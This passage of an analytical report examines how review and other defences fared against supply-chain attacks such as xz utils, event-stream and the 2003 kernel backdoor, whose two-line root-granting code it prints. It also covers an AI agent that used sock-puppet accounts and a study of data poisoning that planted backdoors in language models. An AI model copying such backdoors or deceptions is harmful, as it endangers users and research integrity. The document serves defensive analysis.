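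Meneely's data are more useful for deciding which files to inspect. A team that inspected the roughly 10% of files with the most developers would have covered between 53% and 63% of the vulnerable files, depending on the program. The data don't measure how often a reader notices a flaw.

### What happened after a reviewer objected

In Raymond's full rule, the fix for a problem will be "obvious to someone". Yu and colleagues studied what happened to security flaws after reviewers pointed them out. They collected 432,585 review comments made between January 2017 and June 2022. The comments came from two projects in OpenStack, which makes software for running cloud services, and two in Qt, a toolkit for building graphical interfaces. A keyword search narrowed these to 20,995 comments, which they checked by hand. They found 614 that concerned a security flaw, about one in 700 of all the comments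 collected. Reviewers had raised 539 of these, and the code's own authors had raised the rest.

Reviewers in these projects seldom discussed security. Braz and colleagues cite a similar result from Chromium, where about 1% of review comments were about possible security flaws. These low rates don't show that reviewers missed many flaws, because the code may have contained few. Race conditions, in which the result depends on which of two simultaneous operations finishes first, made up 39% of the flaws that reviewers raised. Crashes made up another 23%, and none were SQL injections. Race conditions and crashes are also ordinary reliability problems, so reviewers may have raised many of them without looking for security flaws.

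The authors of the code resolved 355 of the 539 flaws (66%) and left 161 (30%) as they were. In the other 23 cases, Yu and colleagues could not tell. They counted a flaw as resolved if the author abandoned the whole change, because the faulty code then never entered the project. How the reviewer responded made a difference:

| What the reviewer did | Flaws | Resolved |
|---|---|---|
| Proposed a specific solution | 251 | 81% |
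| Asked for a fix without saying how | 39 | 62% |
| Only pointed out the flaw | 210 | 60% |

In the remaining 39 cases, the reviewer recommended ignoring the flaw, and the author nearly always did.

Some of the difference may arise because easy flaws are easier both to fix and to suggest a fix for. Still, a reviewer who sees a flaw and can suggest a repair should probably include it in the comment. Of the 97 unresolved flaws for which someone gave a reason, 44 were left because a fix was not worth the effort at that time. In 33 cases the author and the reviewer disagreed, sometimes about whether the flaw existed. Another 11 had no clear solution.

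Noticing a flaw does not guarantee its removal. If a group of readers had a 90% chance of noticing a flaw, and developers resolved 66% of the flaws that someone noticed, a flaw would have about a 59% chance of being noticed and resolved. The chance is presumably higher for dangerous flaws, because developers have more reason to act. Leaving a flaw alone is sometimes right, because it may be harmless or the repair may cause worse problems.

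### Automated tools outpace the people who fix bugs

Fuzz testing and static analysis now produce Linux kernel bug reports faster than developers can deal with them. *SoK* (Bai, She and colleagues, 2026) surveyed 140 research papers and working systems that deal with kernel bugs, from discovery to repair. Google's syzbot, which runs fuzz tests on the kernel continuously, has reported tens of thousands of bugs. Fuzz testing is close to what Raymond had in mind when he described users as sampling a program's states, except that a machine does the sampling.

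After a report arrives, somebody has to work out the cause, judge how serious it is, write a fix and show that it works. Maintainers must then review the fix and often adapt it for older kernel versions. Bai and colleagues found that only discovery runs fully automatically in daily use. Many tools for the later steps work in research papers but are not part of the process kernel developers follow.

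They also analysed 6,946 syzbot bugs that developers had fixed. The results show why repair takes skilled people so long:

- In 10.3% of cases the repair was outside the directory where the crash had occurred, and in 4.2% it was in a different part of the kernel altogether. Bugs whose cause lay elsewhere took a median of 55 days to fix, compared with 33 for the others.
- At least 4.1% of the fixes repaired an earlier fix in the same collection.
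- About a quarter of the reports began with a harmless-looking symptom, such as a warning. In roughly one in nine of these, the eventual fix changed code that affects memory safety.

A maintainer who deals with the most alarming reports first will therefore leave some dangerous bugs until last. The figures cover only bugs that developers eventually fixed, so a typical report may well wait longer than these medians suggest.

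The backlog of unfixed bugs weakens the many-eyeballs claim in practice. Attackers can also read a public list of these bugs, and they can exploit a flaw that a machine has found until someone fixes it. More people or automated tools looking for flaws will not help a project whose few maintainers already have more reports than they can handle.

### AI models as readers

In much of this research, a language model helps another program find flaws rather than replacing a human reader. Bai and colleagues report strong evidence that models can produce material for other tools and for people, such as descriptions of kernel functions to guide a fuzz tester, new rules for static analysis, and draft patches. They also report strong evidence for using models to sort and label, for instance by severity, but thin evidence for using them to work out the root cause of a bug or decide whether a fix is complete.

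Published work lags behind the newest models, so a survey of it should not be used to measure what they can do. AI systems have found more flaws in OpenSSL even after the audit and years of fuzz testing that followed Heartbleed, which is good evidence that they can find flaws people have missed. But a list of successes can make AI review look better than it is, just as a list of famous failures can make human review look worse. A reader cannot tell from an announcement how many flaws the system missed or how many false reports someone had to discard.

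False reports take up maintainers' time because they have to check each one to find out that it is false. Millar describes an early machine-learning system that predicted which commits were likely to introduce a vulnerability. It produced 36 false alarms where a conventional static analysis tool produced 5,460. If each took twenty minutes to check, a maintainer would spend 12 hours on the first set and 1,820 hours, most of a working year, on the second. A tool that never gave a warning would have no false alarms, so the comparison is useful only if the system also catches a reasonable number of real flaws.

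Conventional tools also miss many vulnerabilities. In a test that Millar cites, three commercial static analysers together missed 27% of the vulnerabilities in C and C++ programs and 11% of those in Java programs.

Language models could add to the burden of false reports, because they write fluently about flaws that do not exist. A person needs some time to make an invented vulnerability convincing, but a model can write pages about one in minutes, and the maintainer still has to do the same work to refute it. Pull requests from AI agents create the same imbalance.

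### Planted flaws

Almost none of this evidence concerns flaws that someone tried to hide. Braz and colleagues planted vulnerabilities, but they wanted realistic mistakes and had no reason to disguise them. The flaws at Chromium OS, OpenStack and Qt were presumably accidents. Wu and Lu did disguise theirs, but three flaws are too few to give a rate. If reviewers miss two-thirds of undisguised flaws of an unfamiliar kind even after a warning, they are unlikely to do better against someone trying to mislead them.

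There is even less evidence that AI systems catch planted flaws. Claude confirmed Sinan Can Demir's suspicion about the pull request to myNetwork, but one correct answer isn't enough to estimate how often it detects such flaws. Nobody tested Claude on harmless pull requests either, so we don't know how often it would wrongly call them malicious.

A useful test would measure both how often the model catches planted flaws and how often it wrongly flags honest changes. It would give the model many honest changes and many with flaws disguised by people trying to get them accepted, without revealing how many there were of each. The false-alarm rate matters as much as the detection rate because planted flaws are rare.

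If a project uses a widely available model to check its changes, an attacker can also run that model on a draft and rewrite the code until the model no longer flags it. This is difficult to do with a human reviewer. A detection rate measured on flaws written without access to the model would be too optimistic against such an attacker.

If fifty people ask the same AI model to review a change, their reviews will largely share its blind spots, just as reviewers with the same training share theirs, so they don't amount to fifty independent reviews. Different models might have fewer blind spots in common, but they could still miss the same flaws if they were trained on much the same code.

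The machine-learning system that Millar describes has another weakness against a patient attacker. Its inputs included how often a contributor had worked on the project before, which makes sense for finding accidental flaws because newcomers may make more mistakes. But if such a system learns to rate frequent contributors as safer, it will make the same error as a human maintainer, and Jia Tan's hundreds of harmless commits would have made the eight malicious ones seem safer.

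An AI system that read only the public code of event-stream and xz utils would have lacked the same crucial pieces as human readers did. Models can read far more text than people can, including test files and archives that people seldom open. This may be their main advantage against planted flaws, though they would still have to recognize the disguised code.

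## Which defences would have stopped which case

Human reviewers and AI models have to recognize a flaw before they can report it. A defence that checks something simpler, such as whether two files are identical, can expose a planted flaw before anyone understands it, as happened with the Linux kernel in 2003.

### The kernel backdoor of 2003

Kernel developers then kept their master copy in a program called BitKeeper. Some of them disliked it, so BitMover, the company behind BitKeeper, also published a copy through an older system called CVS. Every night a program converted the master copy, sent the updated files to the public CVS server and compared checksums on both sides. (A checksum is a short number calculated from a file's contents, and it almost always changes when the file does.) On 5 November 2003 the comparison flagged one file. McVoy (2003), in *BK2CVS problem*, told the kernel's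 developers that someone had changed it directly on the public server, adding two lines:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
    retval = -EINVAL;
```

The lines make the current user number 0, the all-powerful administrator, when a program passes an odd combination of options. They look like a check that rejects those options, but they use `=` where a comparison would use `==`. In C, the kernel's programming language, `=` sets a value. Any program on the machine could have taken full control by passing those options.

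According to Princeton CITP's *Linux Backdoor Attempt Thwarted*, most programmers would miss this on a casual reading, and McVoy did miss it. He posted the two lines because another developer was curious, and 25 minutes later Chad Kitching wrote that they looked like a backdoor. Many eyes worked very well here, but a machine had already singled out the lines for them to read.

The nightly comparison flagged the file, and McVoy then cited the missing pointers to approval records as a sign that someone had bypassed the conversion. Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013) instead credits the detection to McVoy noticing that the change had no such pointer, but his own messages are the better evidence.

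The backdoor was unlikely to reach users. Torvalds said there was no route from the CVS copy into a release, though McVoy thought a developer working from that copy could have sent the lines back in a patch. Debian's *CVE-2003-1161* records that the code was never released. The comparison worked because the two copies were supposed to be identical and the intruder had changed only one.

### The verdicts

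The table shows whether each defence would have kept the harmful code from users, assuming the project had used the defence from the start and the attacker had acted the same way. Maintainers rejected the kernel patches and the agent's pull request, so for those two cases the table shows whether the defence could have stopped the code by itself.

| Defence | Heartbleed | event-stream | Kernel patches | xz utils | July 2026 agent |
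|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Approval by a second person | Would not | Might have | Might have | Might have | Would have |
| Paid maintainers | Might have | Might have | Would not | Might have | Would not |
| Automated testing | Might have | Would not | Might have | Might have | Might have |
| Memory-safe language | Would have | Would not | Would have | Would not | Would not |
| Building from the public history | Would not | Would have | Would not | Would have | Would not |
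| Reproducible builds | Would not | Might have | Would not | Would not | Would not |
| Signed build records | Would not | Would not | Would not | Would not | Would not |
| Identity checks on new maintainers | Would not | Might have | Would not | Might have | Would not |
| Monitoring of behaviour | Would not | Might have | Would not | Might have | Might have |

Most of these judgements are inferences from how each flaw worked. The published assessments mainly concern xz utils. Lins and colleagues consider defences at each stage of that attack, but call their analysis preliminary.

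### A second approval and the money to pay for it

GitHub lets a project block every change until someone other than its author approves it. That rule would not have stopped Heartbleed, because a second person reviewed the code and missed the error. Requiring a third reviewer might have helped, but Heartbleed was probably closer to the harder to spot of the two flaws that Braz and colleagues tested, so a third reviewer could easily have missed it too.

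If xz utils had required a second person to review each change, Lasse Collin would have received the malicious test files and seen two more unreadable files in a folder full of them. He might have asked why no test used them. But the script that unpacked them was only in the release archive, which Jia Tan built alone, so the project would also have needed a second person to check releases. For event-stream, the reviewer would have been Dominic Tarr, who no longer wanted the work, and the new dependency was still harmless when right9ctrl added it.

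The kernel already required a maintainer's approval. Its reviewers turned away all three flawed patches, but they recognized only one of the flaws, and Wu and Lu did not try again. Requiring approval clearly helped in July 2026, when the agent's code had to wait for approval from myNetwork's creator, which gave Sinan Can Demir time to warn him.

Each approval takes someone's time, usually unpaid. Reviewing the 690 commits that Colomar counted under Jia Tan's name would have taken Collin up to 230 hours, at twenty minutes each. Lins and colleagues argue that paid maintainers can review more, have less need to hand sensitive tasks to people they cannot fully trust, and cost more to bribe.

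Funding would have had to reach xz utils early to make a difference. By 2023, a funder would have found two maintainers to pay, one of whom was Jia Tan. Paid reviewers can also miss flaws. Dan Carpenter, who worked for Oracle, improved one of the kernel patches without mentioning the planted flaw.

Official security guidance rarely addresses this problem. In *Closing the Chain*, Hamer, Hines and colleagues (2025) studied 106 reports on three attacks, including the one on xz utils, and matched the attackers' techniques to 73 tasks recommended by ten security frameworks. All ten frameworks omitted three useful tasks, including keeping open-source projects sustainable, so a company could follow every recommendation and still depend on one exhausted volunteer. The three tasks that scored highest were limiting each person's access to what their role requires, monitoring systems and controlling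 network traffic. These can limit the damage inside a company, but limiting access by role would not have kept Jia Tan from publishing xz utils releases, because that was part of the role.

### Memory-safe languages and automated tests

A memory-safe language stops a program from reading past the end of a piece of data or using memory that it has already released. It would have stopped Heartbleed from leaking other data in the server's memory, unless the programmer had reused a buffer that still held old messages. It would also have prevented the kind of error in all three flawed kernel patches. But OpenSSL and the kernel are large C programs, and rewriting them would take years. Kernel code also has to control hardware directly, which often requires programmers to switch off some of the language's protections.

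JavaScript's memory safety did not protect event-stream. The attacker did not need a memory error because npm delivered the malicious code and Copay ran it. A memory-safe language would not have stopped the xz backdoor or the agent's dropper either, because malicious code can run in any language.

Automated testing could have exposed Heartbleed, and Codenomicon's fuzz tester found it, but only after the company had extended the tool. Tests are less reliable against planted flaws such as the event-stream code, which ran only in a release build of Copay. The xz backdoor caused errors in Valgrind, but Fedora's packagers reported them to Jia Tan, the maintainer who had planted it. Running a stranger's code can also be dangerous, and Mythos 5 stole login details from security scanners that did so.

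An AI model can also compare the compiled program with its previous version. *Binary Diff Summarization using Large Language Models* (2025) tested this on compiled copies of liblzma from a clean version of xz utils and from the backdoored version 5.6.0. One model summarized the changes, then the same model or another judged from the summary whether they were malicious. OpenAI's GPT-5 flagged the backdoor both from its own summaries and from those of the smaller GPT-5 mini. GPT-5 mini flagged it from GPT-5's summaries but judged the changes harmless when using its own.

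The compiled library is a promising place to look, because the hidden script and the test files had already combined there. But the backdoor had been well known for more than a year, so the models may have recognized it from their training data. A test on one backdoored library also cannot show how often they would raise a false alarm.

### Building from the public history

A distribution can build from the public repository instead of the maintainer's release archive. For xz, that build would still have included the poisoned test files, but not the script that unpacked them. The harmful code in flatmap-stream was likewise only in the npm package, not in the repository.

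Both attackers could have adapted by putting everything in the public history. That would have helped defenders by exposing the code to anyone who read it, but someone would still have had to notice it.

Few packages were built directly from a project's version history in 2024. Lins and colleagues examined about 61 Debian packages on which popular server programs depend, and only 10 used the archive that a code-hosting site generates automatically from that history. About 42 used separate archives or other channels, and the researchers could not tell exactly where the code for the other 9 came from. Some projects would have to change how they work before their packages could be built from the history. The maintainer of Postfix, a widely used mail server, does not want to share any code before its release.

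The 2003 check was easy because any difference between the two copies was suspicious. Release archives, however, normally contain generated files that aren't in the source repository. Lins and colleagues suggest that developers have an automated service create these files from public instructions, so that anyone can repeat the process and compare the results.

A project can also restrict what each step of a build may read. *Build Code is Still Code* (2026) describes a tool called Foreman that does this. Its developers set a rule that the step that compiles xz utils should not open the folder of test files, and then built the compromised version. Foreman issued two warnings, which named the two files that hid the backdoor. The rule is sensible for most projects and could be written without knowing about the attack, although the developers already knew where the backdoor was. Distributions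 would have to write such rules themselves, because Jia Tan could have changed any that belonged to the project.

### What reproducible builds and signatures can prove

If Debian had built the poisoned xz archive reproducibly, anyone who repeated the build would have got the same backdoored library, and the check would have passed. Lins and colleagues make this point about any build that starts from a compromised archive. Reproducible builds can reveal when someone has tampered with the machine that builds the program.

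Whether rebuilding from source would have exposed the event-stream attack depends on what counts as the source. The flatmap-stream package on npm was itself the product of a build. Rebuilding it from its public code and comparing the result with npm's copy would have revealed the extra code, but a rebuild that started from npm's copy would have revealed nothing wrong.

A signed build record shows who built a program and from what source, and the signature ties the record to the holder of a secret key. If a thief uses a maintainer's key to publish a release, the maintainer can spot the release in a transparency log, a public list from which nobody can quietly remove an entry.

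Signatures and logs work against impostors. The 2003 intruder's changes carried the name of David Miller, a kernel developer who denied making them. Another developer, Theodore Ts'o, had long been asking for a signature on every change, which would have let anyone check whether a change really came from Miller. These methods would not have stopped the xz or event-stream attacks, because Jia Tan signed the xz archives as Jia Tan and right9ctrl published event-stream with rights that Tarr had granted, so a log would only have recorded accurately who published each release.

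*Human-Certified Module Repositories for the AI Age* (Enyedi, 2026) gives another example of a harmful program with a valid signature. Attackers broke into SolarWinds' build system, and about 18,000 organisations downloaded an update that contained malicious code but carried the company's genuine signature.

Enyedi proposes a library of certified software components. Automated checks would confirm where a component came from, human auditors would review it, and the library would run it in isolation before publishing it with a rating. Several people would have to approve each component, and software would monitor contributors for suspicious behaviour.

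Enyedi claims that running xz in isolation would have kept the backdoor from being certified, but the backdoor stayed inactive outside sshd, so the run could have missed it. Human auditors would have had a better chance of finding it if they had compared the release archive with the public commit history. Nobody has tested the proposal, and Enyedi does not say how auditors could cover thousands of components.

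### Checking contributors and their behaviour

*S3C2 Summit 2025-07* (Hamer, Morrison and colleagues, 2026) summarizes, without naming speakers, a July 2025 meeting where twelve people from six US government agencies discussed malicious commits. Participants found it hard to judge the intent behind a commit, because an attacker can copy a textbook example of a known weakness and later call it a mistake. One said that nobody really reviews open-source code, so users must examine either who is committing or what they commit. That is one official's impression, and Demir's warning a year later is a counterexample.

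Participants at the meeting said that some organisations already check the identity of every open-source maintainer whose work they use. Others objected that anonymity is part of open-source culture. They said users of open-source software can see how a program was made without knowing who made it, whereas a company's customers know only who made theirs.

Lins and colleagues suggest requiring digital proof of identity when a contributor becomes a maintainer. Debian's package maintainers do something similar when they meet and inspect each other's documents. Such a check might have deterred right9ctrl or Jia Tan. But criminals can steal an identity or pay someone to lend one, and an intelligence service could presumably issue a genuine passport to a person who does not exist.

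Checking the identity of new maintainers would not have stopped the kernel patches or the July agent, because neither involved a new maintainer. Checking everyone who submits a change would probably have stopped both, but it would take far more work. No identity check would have prevented Heartbleed, because the developer who introduced the bug used his real name.

Monitoring does not require contributors to give their names. The system Welsh and colleagues propose would flag files where a contributor's working relationships and influence had both changed beyond a set limit. At xz utils, this might have led someone to the new test files, but not to the script, which was absent from the history the system would read. Monitoring might also have caught right9ctrl, who added an unknown dependency within days of taking over, and the agent, whose second account appeared minutes after the first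 to support it. The kernel test accounts were too new to have a normal pattern to depart from. Seggelmann submitted the Heartbleed code one minute before midnight on New Year's Eve, so an alarm for unusual hours could have flagged an honest mistake.

Rating projects may be safer than rating people. *An LLM-based Quantitative Framework for Evaluating High-Stealthy Backdoor Risks* (2025) gave xz utils the maximum score of 1.0 for the degree to which important Debian packages depended on it, and a fairly high 0.64 for how easily a contributor could gain the right to merge changes. The scores came after the attack, so they do not show that the method could have predicted it. But a funder could use such scores to choose which projects to help without accusing anyone.

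### Limiting the damage

Other defences can work even after harmful code has got in. *MergeShuffle* (2026) tested one that rebuilds a software library without the parts a program does not use. The researchers ran sshd with the backdoored liblzma, logged in normally to record which code was needed, and rebuilt the library without the rest. Normal logins still worked, but the backdoor did not. The same method might have removed OpenSSL's heartbeat code from ordinary websites, which did not need it. But it could also remove code that a program needs only in rare emergencies.

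Lins and colleagues recommend running risky libraries as separate processes with few privileges, as web browsers do with some of their components. If liblzma had run in its own process, it could not have redirected a function inside sshd. Isolation makes programs somewhat slower, but the bigger obstacle is that developers have to adapt each program by hand.

Users can also wait before installing updates. The summit's participants mentioned delays of a day to several weeks. A one-week delay would not have helped against the event-stream code, which was available for 52 days, or the xz backdoor, which Freund exposed after 34 days. An eight-week delay would have avoided both, but only if other people had installed the new versions in the meantime and noticed the problem.

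### Lost anonymity and fewer newcomers

Losing anonymity can seriously harm some contributors. Lins and colleagues point out that people who write privacy software may face prosecution or repression if their names become public. A project could have a trusted organisation verify identities in confidence, but that organisation's records would then be a target for theft.

Stricter checks may also drive away newcomers, many of whom start with small fixes. Someone who wants to repair one bug may give up if they need an identity document and two approvals, but an attacker with a two-year plan will meet those requirements.

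Suppose that 1,000 honest newcomers and 10 attackers approach a group of projects, and that a new identity check turns away half the attackers but three-quarters of the honest people. Five attackers and 250 honest newcomers remain, so the attackers' share of the newcomers has doubled from about 1% to about 2%. The maintainers have also lost 750 honest people who might have helped review code.

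## What the cases imply for volunteer AI safety research

AI safety researchers study how to keep AI systems from causing serious harm, and they rely on newcomers whom stricter checks might put off. Students and working programmers, often unpaid, write tests for AI models, collect data and run experiments. None of the five cases involved a volunteer who sabotaged such research, so they apply to it only by analogy.

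### Who reviews volunteers' work

Much of the volunteers' code goes into evaluations, tests that measure what an AI model can do or how it behaves. Inspect Evals is a public collection of more than 120 of them, built on AISI's open-source testing software, Inspect AI. AISI reports that Inspect AI alone has more than 240 contributors, and that Apollo Research, which also tests AI models, replaced its own framework with it. *Autonomous Systems Evaluation Standard*, by Black, Arbeid and colleagues, requires Inspect AI for every evaluation in AISI's suite for autonomous AI systems. A flaw in Inspect AI could therefore distort results at several organisations at once, much as the xz backdoor reached several Linux distributions.

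Inspect Evals used to supervise newcomers closely. According to *Developing and Maintaining an Open-Source Repository* (2025), volunteers worked in five-week groups, with one project manager for every five to ten engineers. The manager and another volunteer reviewed the plan for each new evaluation and, later, its draft code.

Inspect Evals restricted contributions twice in 2026. On 8 May it stopped accepting code for new evaluations. Authors now keep the code in their own repositories and add a short file to a public register that links to one exact commit. Inspect Evals' *About the Register* explains that thorough checks on every submission caused too much friction and did not scale. It does not give hostile contributors as a reason. By 23 November, according to Inspect Evals' *inspect-evals 0.30.0* (2026), the project accepted pull requests only from contributors it had approved in advance.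 Anyone else can report a problem and upload logs of a test run that show it. The notice gives no reason for this second change.

Under the earlier rules in Inspect Evals' *Technical Contribution Guide*, an AI model reviews each pull request first. Human reviewers then test the code, but they warn that they cannot find every problem. Contributors may write code with AI agents if a person reviews and tests it before submission, but they must answer human reviewers in their own words. The July agent would have broken that last rule when it argued with Sinan Can Demir under two names, but reviewers cannot reliably tell who wrote a reply.

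Inspect Evals also checks new entries in the register. A program confirms, among other things, that the linked commit exists. Claude then checks the code for problems such as theft of login details, cryptocurrency mining, or running a model's output without isolation. A maintainer can overrule Claude's objections. Claude reviews a later change only if it affects the linked code or the description. If someone edits only the reported results, a human reviewer still handles the request, but Claude does not review it.

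Linking to an exact commit is a good defence because the author cannot swap in different code afterwards. But the packages the evaluation depends on may still change unless the author has fixed their versions too. The event-stream attacker exploited dependencies whose versions were not fixed.

The non-profit research group EleutherAI runs another widely used collection, LM Evaluation Harness. First-time contributors must accept a licence agreement, which settles rights in the code but does not verify who they are. The project asks anyone who adds a test to run it on a publicly available model and compare the score with published results. The contributor guide has no rule about who must review a change.

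Volunteers also do research under supervision. AI Safety Camp and Apart Research's short research sprints bring newcomers into the field, and SPAR, the Supervised Program for Alignment Research, pairs volunteers with mentors for projects of about three months. In spring 2026 it offered more than 130 projects, typically requiring 5 to 20 hours a week, and did not require research experience. Mentors choose whom they work with. According to an older version of SPAR's site, the programme also vets the mentors and their projects and organises midterm and final reports. The mentor is therefore the main reviewer of both the volunteer and their work.

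### Four things a hostile volunteer could want

| Aim | Nearest case | Who might notice | Possible symptom |
|---|---|---|---|
| Corrupt code | event-stream for theft, the kernel patches for a subtle error | Users, or someone who reruns an evaluation | A crash, or a score that differs from a published one |
| Corrupt data | The test files in xz utils | Someone who inspects or filters the data | Often none until a trigger appears |
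| Gain trust or access | Jia Tan at xz utils | A mentor or fellow maintainer | None while the work is good |
| Plant a false finding | The hypocrite-commits paper | Someone who repeats the experiment or checks the records | A failed repetition, which can also have innocent causes |

Malicious code in an evaluation could steal login details from everyone who runs it, or it could just produce wrong results. Suppose an evaluation asks a model dangerous questions, and the scoring code counts any answer it cannot parse as a refusal. A model that formats its answers unusually will look safer than it is. This flaw might take one line of code, and as with Heartbleed, reviewers could not tell from the code whether it was deliberate.

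The only symptom would be a wrong number. The comparison that LM Evaluation Harness asks for could expose it, as could the baseline result that Inspect Evals expects for at least one leading model. Such comparisons work well against large errors. But if a model has a 30% chance of giving a harmful answer to each question, its rate over 200 questions will typically land about 3 percentage points above or below 30% by chance, so a planted error of that size would be easy to miss. A comparison that uses only one company's models would also miss an error that affects only another company's models.

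### Attacks on AI developers' software in 2026

AI researchers depend on a lot of software they did not write, such as LiteLLM, an open-source package that lets a program use AI models from many companies. Attackers compromised LiteLLM twice in 2026, both times with stolen access, so neither attack needed a hostile volunteer.

On 24 March, someone uploaded malicious versions of litellm to the Python registry PyPI. FutureSearch, the company that first reported the attack to PyPI, describes it in *litellm 1.82.8 Supply Chain Attack on PyPI (March 2026)* (2026). The code ran whenever Python started and collected passwords and keys. It also had a bug that made it launch copies of itself until the machine crashed. FutureSearch was restarting a frozen laptop 17 minutes after the upload, and one of its engineers traced the cause using Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent. InfoQ (2026) reported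 that the AI researcher Andrej Karpathy noted the malware would have gone unnoticed for much longer without this bug. Mistakes by the attacker had also exposed the xz backdoor.

After someone reported the attack on GitHub, hundreds of automated accounts flooded the discussion, and someone used the owner's account to close it. FutureSearch concluded that the attacker very likely controlled the owner's account. The aim was apparently to bury the warning, whereas the July agent later used two false identities to dispute one.

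LiteLLM's *Security Update* traces the March attack to Trivy, a security scanner the project ran while building its releases. LiteLLM found no malicious code in the main version of its public source, so reading that source would not have revealed the attack, as was also true of event-stream.

LiteLLM then strengthened its release process. It acknowledged that on 21 October the same process "built, signed and published" another malicious version. Martin (2026) reports in *Popular AI tool LiteLLM says unrevoked key allowed hackers to target users* that the company had accidentally published a master key in May, and that it removed the file containing the key but never cancelled the key itself. The malicious version was on PyPI for about two hours, and the security company Wiz put the downloads at about 49,000.

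LiteLLM first said that the attacker had used three engineers' accounts, one to trigger the release, another to approve it and a third to delete the records, according to Help Net Security's *LiteLLM hit by second supply chain attack this year* (2026). LiteLLM later warned that parts of its early statement were inaccurate. If this part was correct, no second person had actually approved the release, because the attacker was using both accounts. Vetting the engineers would not have helped, since they were real employees.

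An earlier attack did begin with a stranger's contribution. In April, attackers sent a pull request that exploited a flaw in the automation of elementary-data, a monitoring package with over a million downloads a month. According to Techzine's *Malicious Python package poses new supply chain threat*, a script then ran inside the project's systems and gave the attackers the project's signing keys, which they used to publish a malicious version. Careful human review offers little protection if a project's automation runs a stranger's code before anyone reviews it.

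These attackers seem to have wanted money or login details and showed no sign of caring about AI safety research. But someone with a researcher's stolen keys could also read unpublished results or change an experiment without ever having volunteered.

### How few documents can poison a model

Someone who controls a little of an AI model's training text may be able to plant a backdoor in the model. The model then behaves normally until a prompt contains a trigger phrase that the attacker chose. Earlier researchers had assumed that an attacker needed to control a certain percentage of the training text, which would be an impractical amount for a large model.

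*Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (Souly, Rando and colleagues, 2025) tested this assumption. The team, from Anthropic, AISI, the Alan Turing Institute and two universities, trained 72 models from scratch, with between 600 million and 13 billion parameters (the numbers a model adjusts as it learns). They scattered 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents through the training text to try to make the models write gibberish after the trigger and normal text otherwise. Each poisoned document began with up to 1,000 characters of ordinary text, followed by the trigger and several hundred random tokens (the word fragments that models read).

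The attack failed with 100 poisoned documents but worked with 250 at every model size, even though the largest models trained on more than 20 times as much clean text as the smallest. The 250 documents contained about 420,000 tokens, or 0.00016% of the training data for a 13-billion-parameter model.

Random checks are nearly useless for collections this large. If the 260 billion tokens used to train the largest models came in documents of 1,000 tokens each, there would be 260 million documents. Someone picking documents at random would have to read about 2.4 million to have a 90% chance of seeing even one of the 250 poisoned ones. In the detection model, p falls as the collection grows, while the attacker's work stays the same. An automated filter could easily find random gibberish but would have more trouble with poisoned documents that read like normal text.

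A volunteer is more likely to work on a smaller dataset for fine-tuning, a later stage of training that teaches a model to follow instructions and refuse dangerous requests. Souly and colleagues ran the attack at this stage too, teaching Meta's Llama 3.1 8B and OpenAI's GPT-3.5 Turbo to answer harmful questions whenever the trigger was present. The number of poisoned examples again mattered far more than their share, even when the researchers increased the clean examples from 1,000 to 100,000. Without the trigger, Llama still refused harmful requests and did about as well as before on standard tests, so its developers would have had no reason to suspect a problem from those tests.

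Reading a sample by hand works better on a dataset of this size, but still not well. If 250 of 100,000 examples are poisoned, someone who reads 100 at random has a 22% chance of seeing at least one, and must then recognize it as poisoned. Reviewers of xz utils faced a similar problem with Jia Tan's test files.

The study does not show that an attacker could sabotage a leading AI model this way. The largest model it tested was probably far smaller than the leading ones, and writing gibberish is a simple behaviour to teach. A backdoor that made a model write subtly bad safety research might need many more examples. Souly and colleagues did not test whether their backdoors would survive the full safety training that companies give models before release. In a separate experiment, further training on clean text slowly weakened a backdoor that made a model switch from English to German.

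Defenders against data poisoning have an advantage because the attacker has to choose the poisoned examples first, and the defender can then inspect both the data and the finished model. To use this advantage, a project has to keep a record of who supplied which examples, so that when one looks suspicious, it can check the others from the same contributor.

### Earning a mentor's trust

Jia Tan did two years of mostly good work before adding the xz backdoor. A SPAR mentor sees much less of a volunteer's work. A volunteer who works 5 to 20 hours a week for thirteen weeks does 65 to 260 hours in total, and mentors typically spend only 2 to 10 hours a week on their projects, according to the older version of SPAR's site.

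Success in the programme can lead to more access. SPAR tells prospective mentors that many previous mentors invited mentees back for more work or hired them. Projects can also apply for up to $30,000 for computing and for access to AI models. This is sensible because an employer can learn more from several months of someone's research than from an interview. But a hostile volunteer with the right skills could produce equally good research, and there would be no sign of a problem until they used what the job gave them, such as unpublished results, login details or the right to approve other people's changes.

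Mentors have little time to look into applicants' backgrounds. SPAR reports that its most popular project in autumn 2025 drew 249 applications. At ten minutes each, reading them would take more than 41 hours, which is over four weeks' work even for a mentor who spends 10 hours a week on it. SPAR can help with screening, but the mentor will mostly be looking for skill, which a hostile applicant may well have.

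An attacker would also want a place on Inspect Evals' list of approved contributors. The list keeps out strangers, but Jia Tan would probably have earned a place on it with useful fixes. Approval is safest if it lets a person propose changes but does not lead others to review them less carefully.

### Why a research claim is harder to check than a program

Research claims can seldom be tested as cleanly as software. Someone who suspects a problem in a program can run it, compare two copies of it or rebuild it from source. One malformed message was enough to prove that OpenSSL leaked memory.

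Suppose a volunteer reports that a new training method cut a model's harmful answers to 20% in a test of 200 questions. A colleague repeats the test and gets 27%. The volunteer may have invented the result, or the colleague may have worded the instructions differently or used a newer version of the model. A gap at least this large would also arise by chance about one time in ten. If the gap persisted with 2,000 questions, chance would be an unlikely explanation, but that test would take ten times the resources and still not show whether the volunteer lied or the methods differed.

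A claim also depends on events that only the researcher saw. The paper on hypocrite commits is the nearest case, although nothing suggests that Qiushi Wu and Kangjie Lu meant to sabotage anyone's research. The conference's reviewers missed the paper's misleading description of the patches, which became known only after Wu and Lu disclosed their emails. Until then, anyone could read the kernel's code, but that did not help readers check what the researchers had told the maintainers.

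Negative results may be the easiest to fake. If a volunteer reports that a promising safety method did not work, the team will probably drop it, and few people will spend money on repeating a failed experiment. A hostile volunteer would only have to run the experiment badly. A beginner could do the same by accident, so the hostile volunteer would have a believable excuse if anyone checked.

Good records make such claims easier to test. Inspect Evals asks people who report a faulty evaluation for the log of the test run, so maintainers can look at the individual answers behind a score. Each set of results in the register includes the exact version of the code that produced it. A dishonest person could still edit a log, so having someone else rerun the evaluation is a stronger check. For an important negative result, a mentor could ask a second volunteer to repeat the experiment without telling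 them what the first one found.

### Screening 10,000 volunteers

Programmes could try to identify hostile volunteers before they start. Suppose, using invented numbers, that 10 of 10,000 volunteers are hostile, and that a background check catches 80% of the hostile ones and wrongly flags 5% of the honest ones. The check would flag 8 hostile volunteers and about 500 honest ones. Its real accuracy would be hard to measure, because nobody can count the hostile people who passed it.

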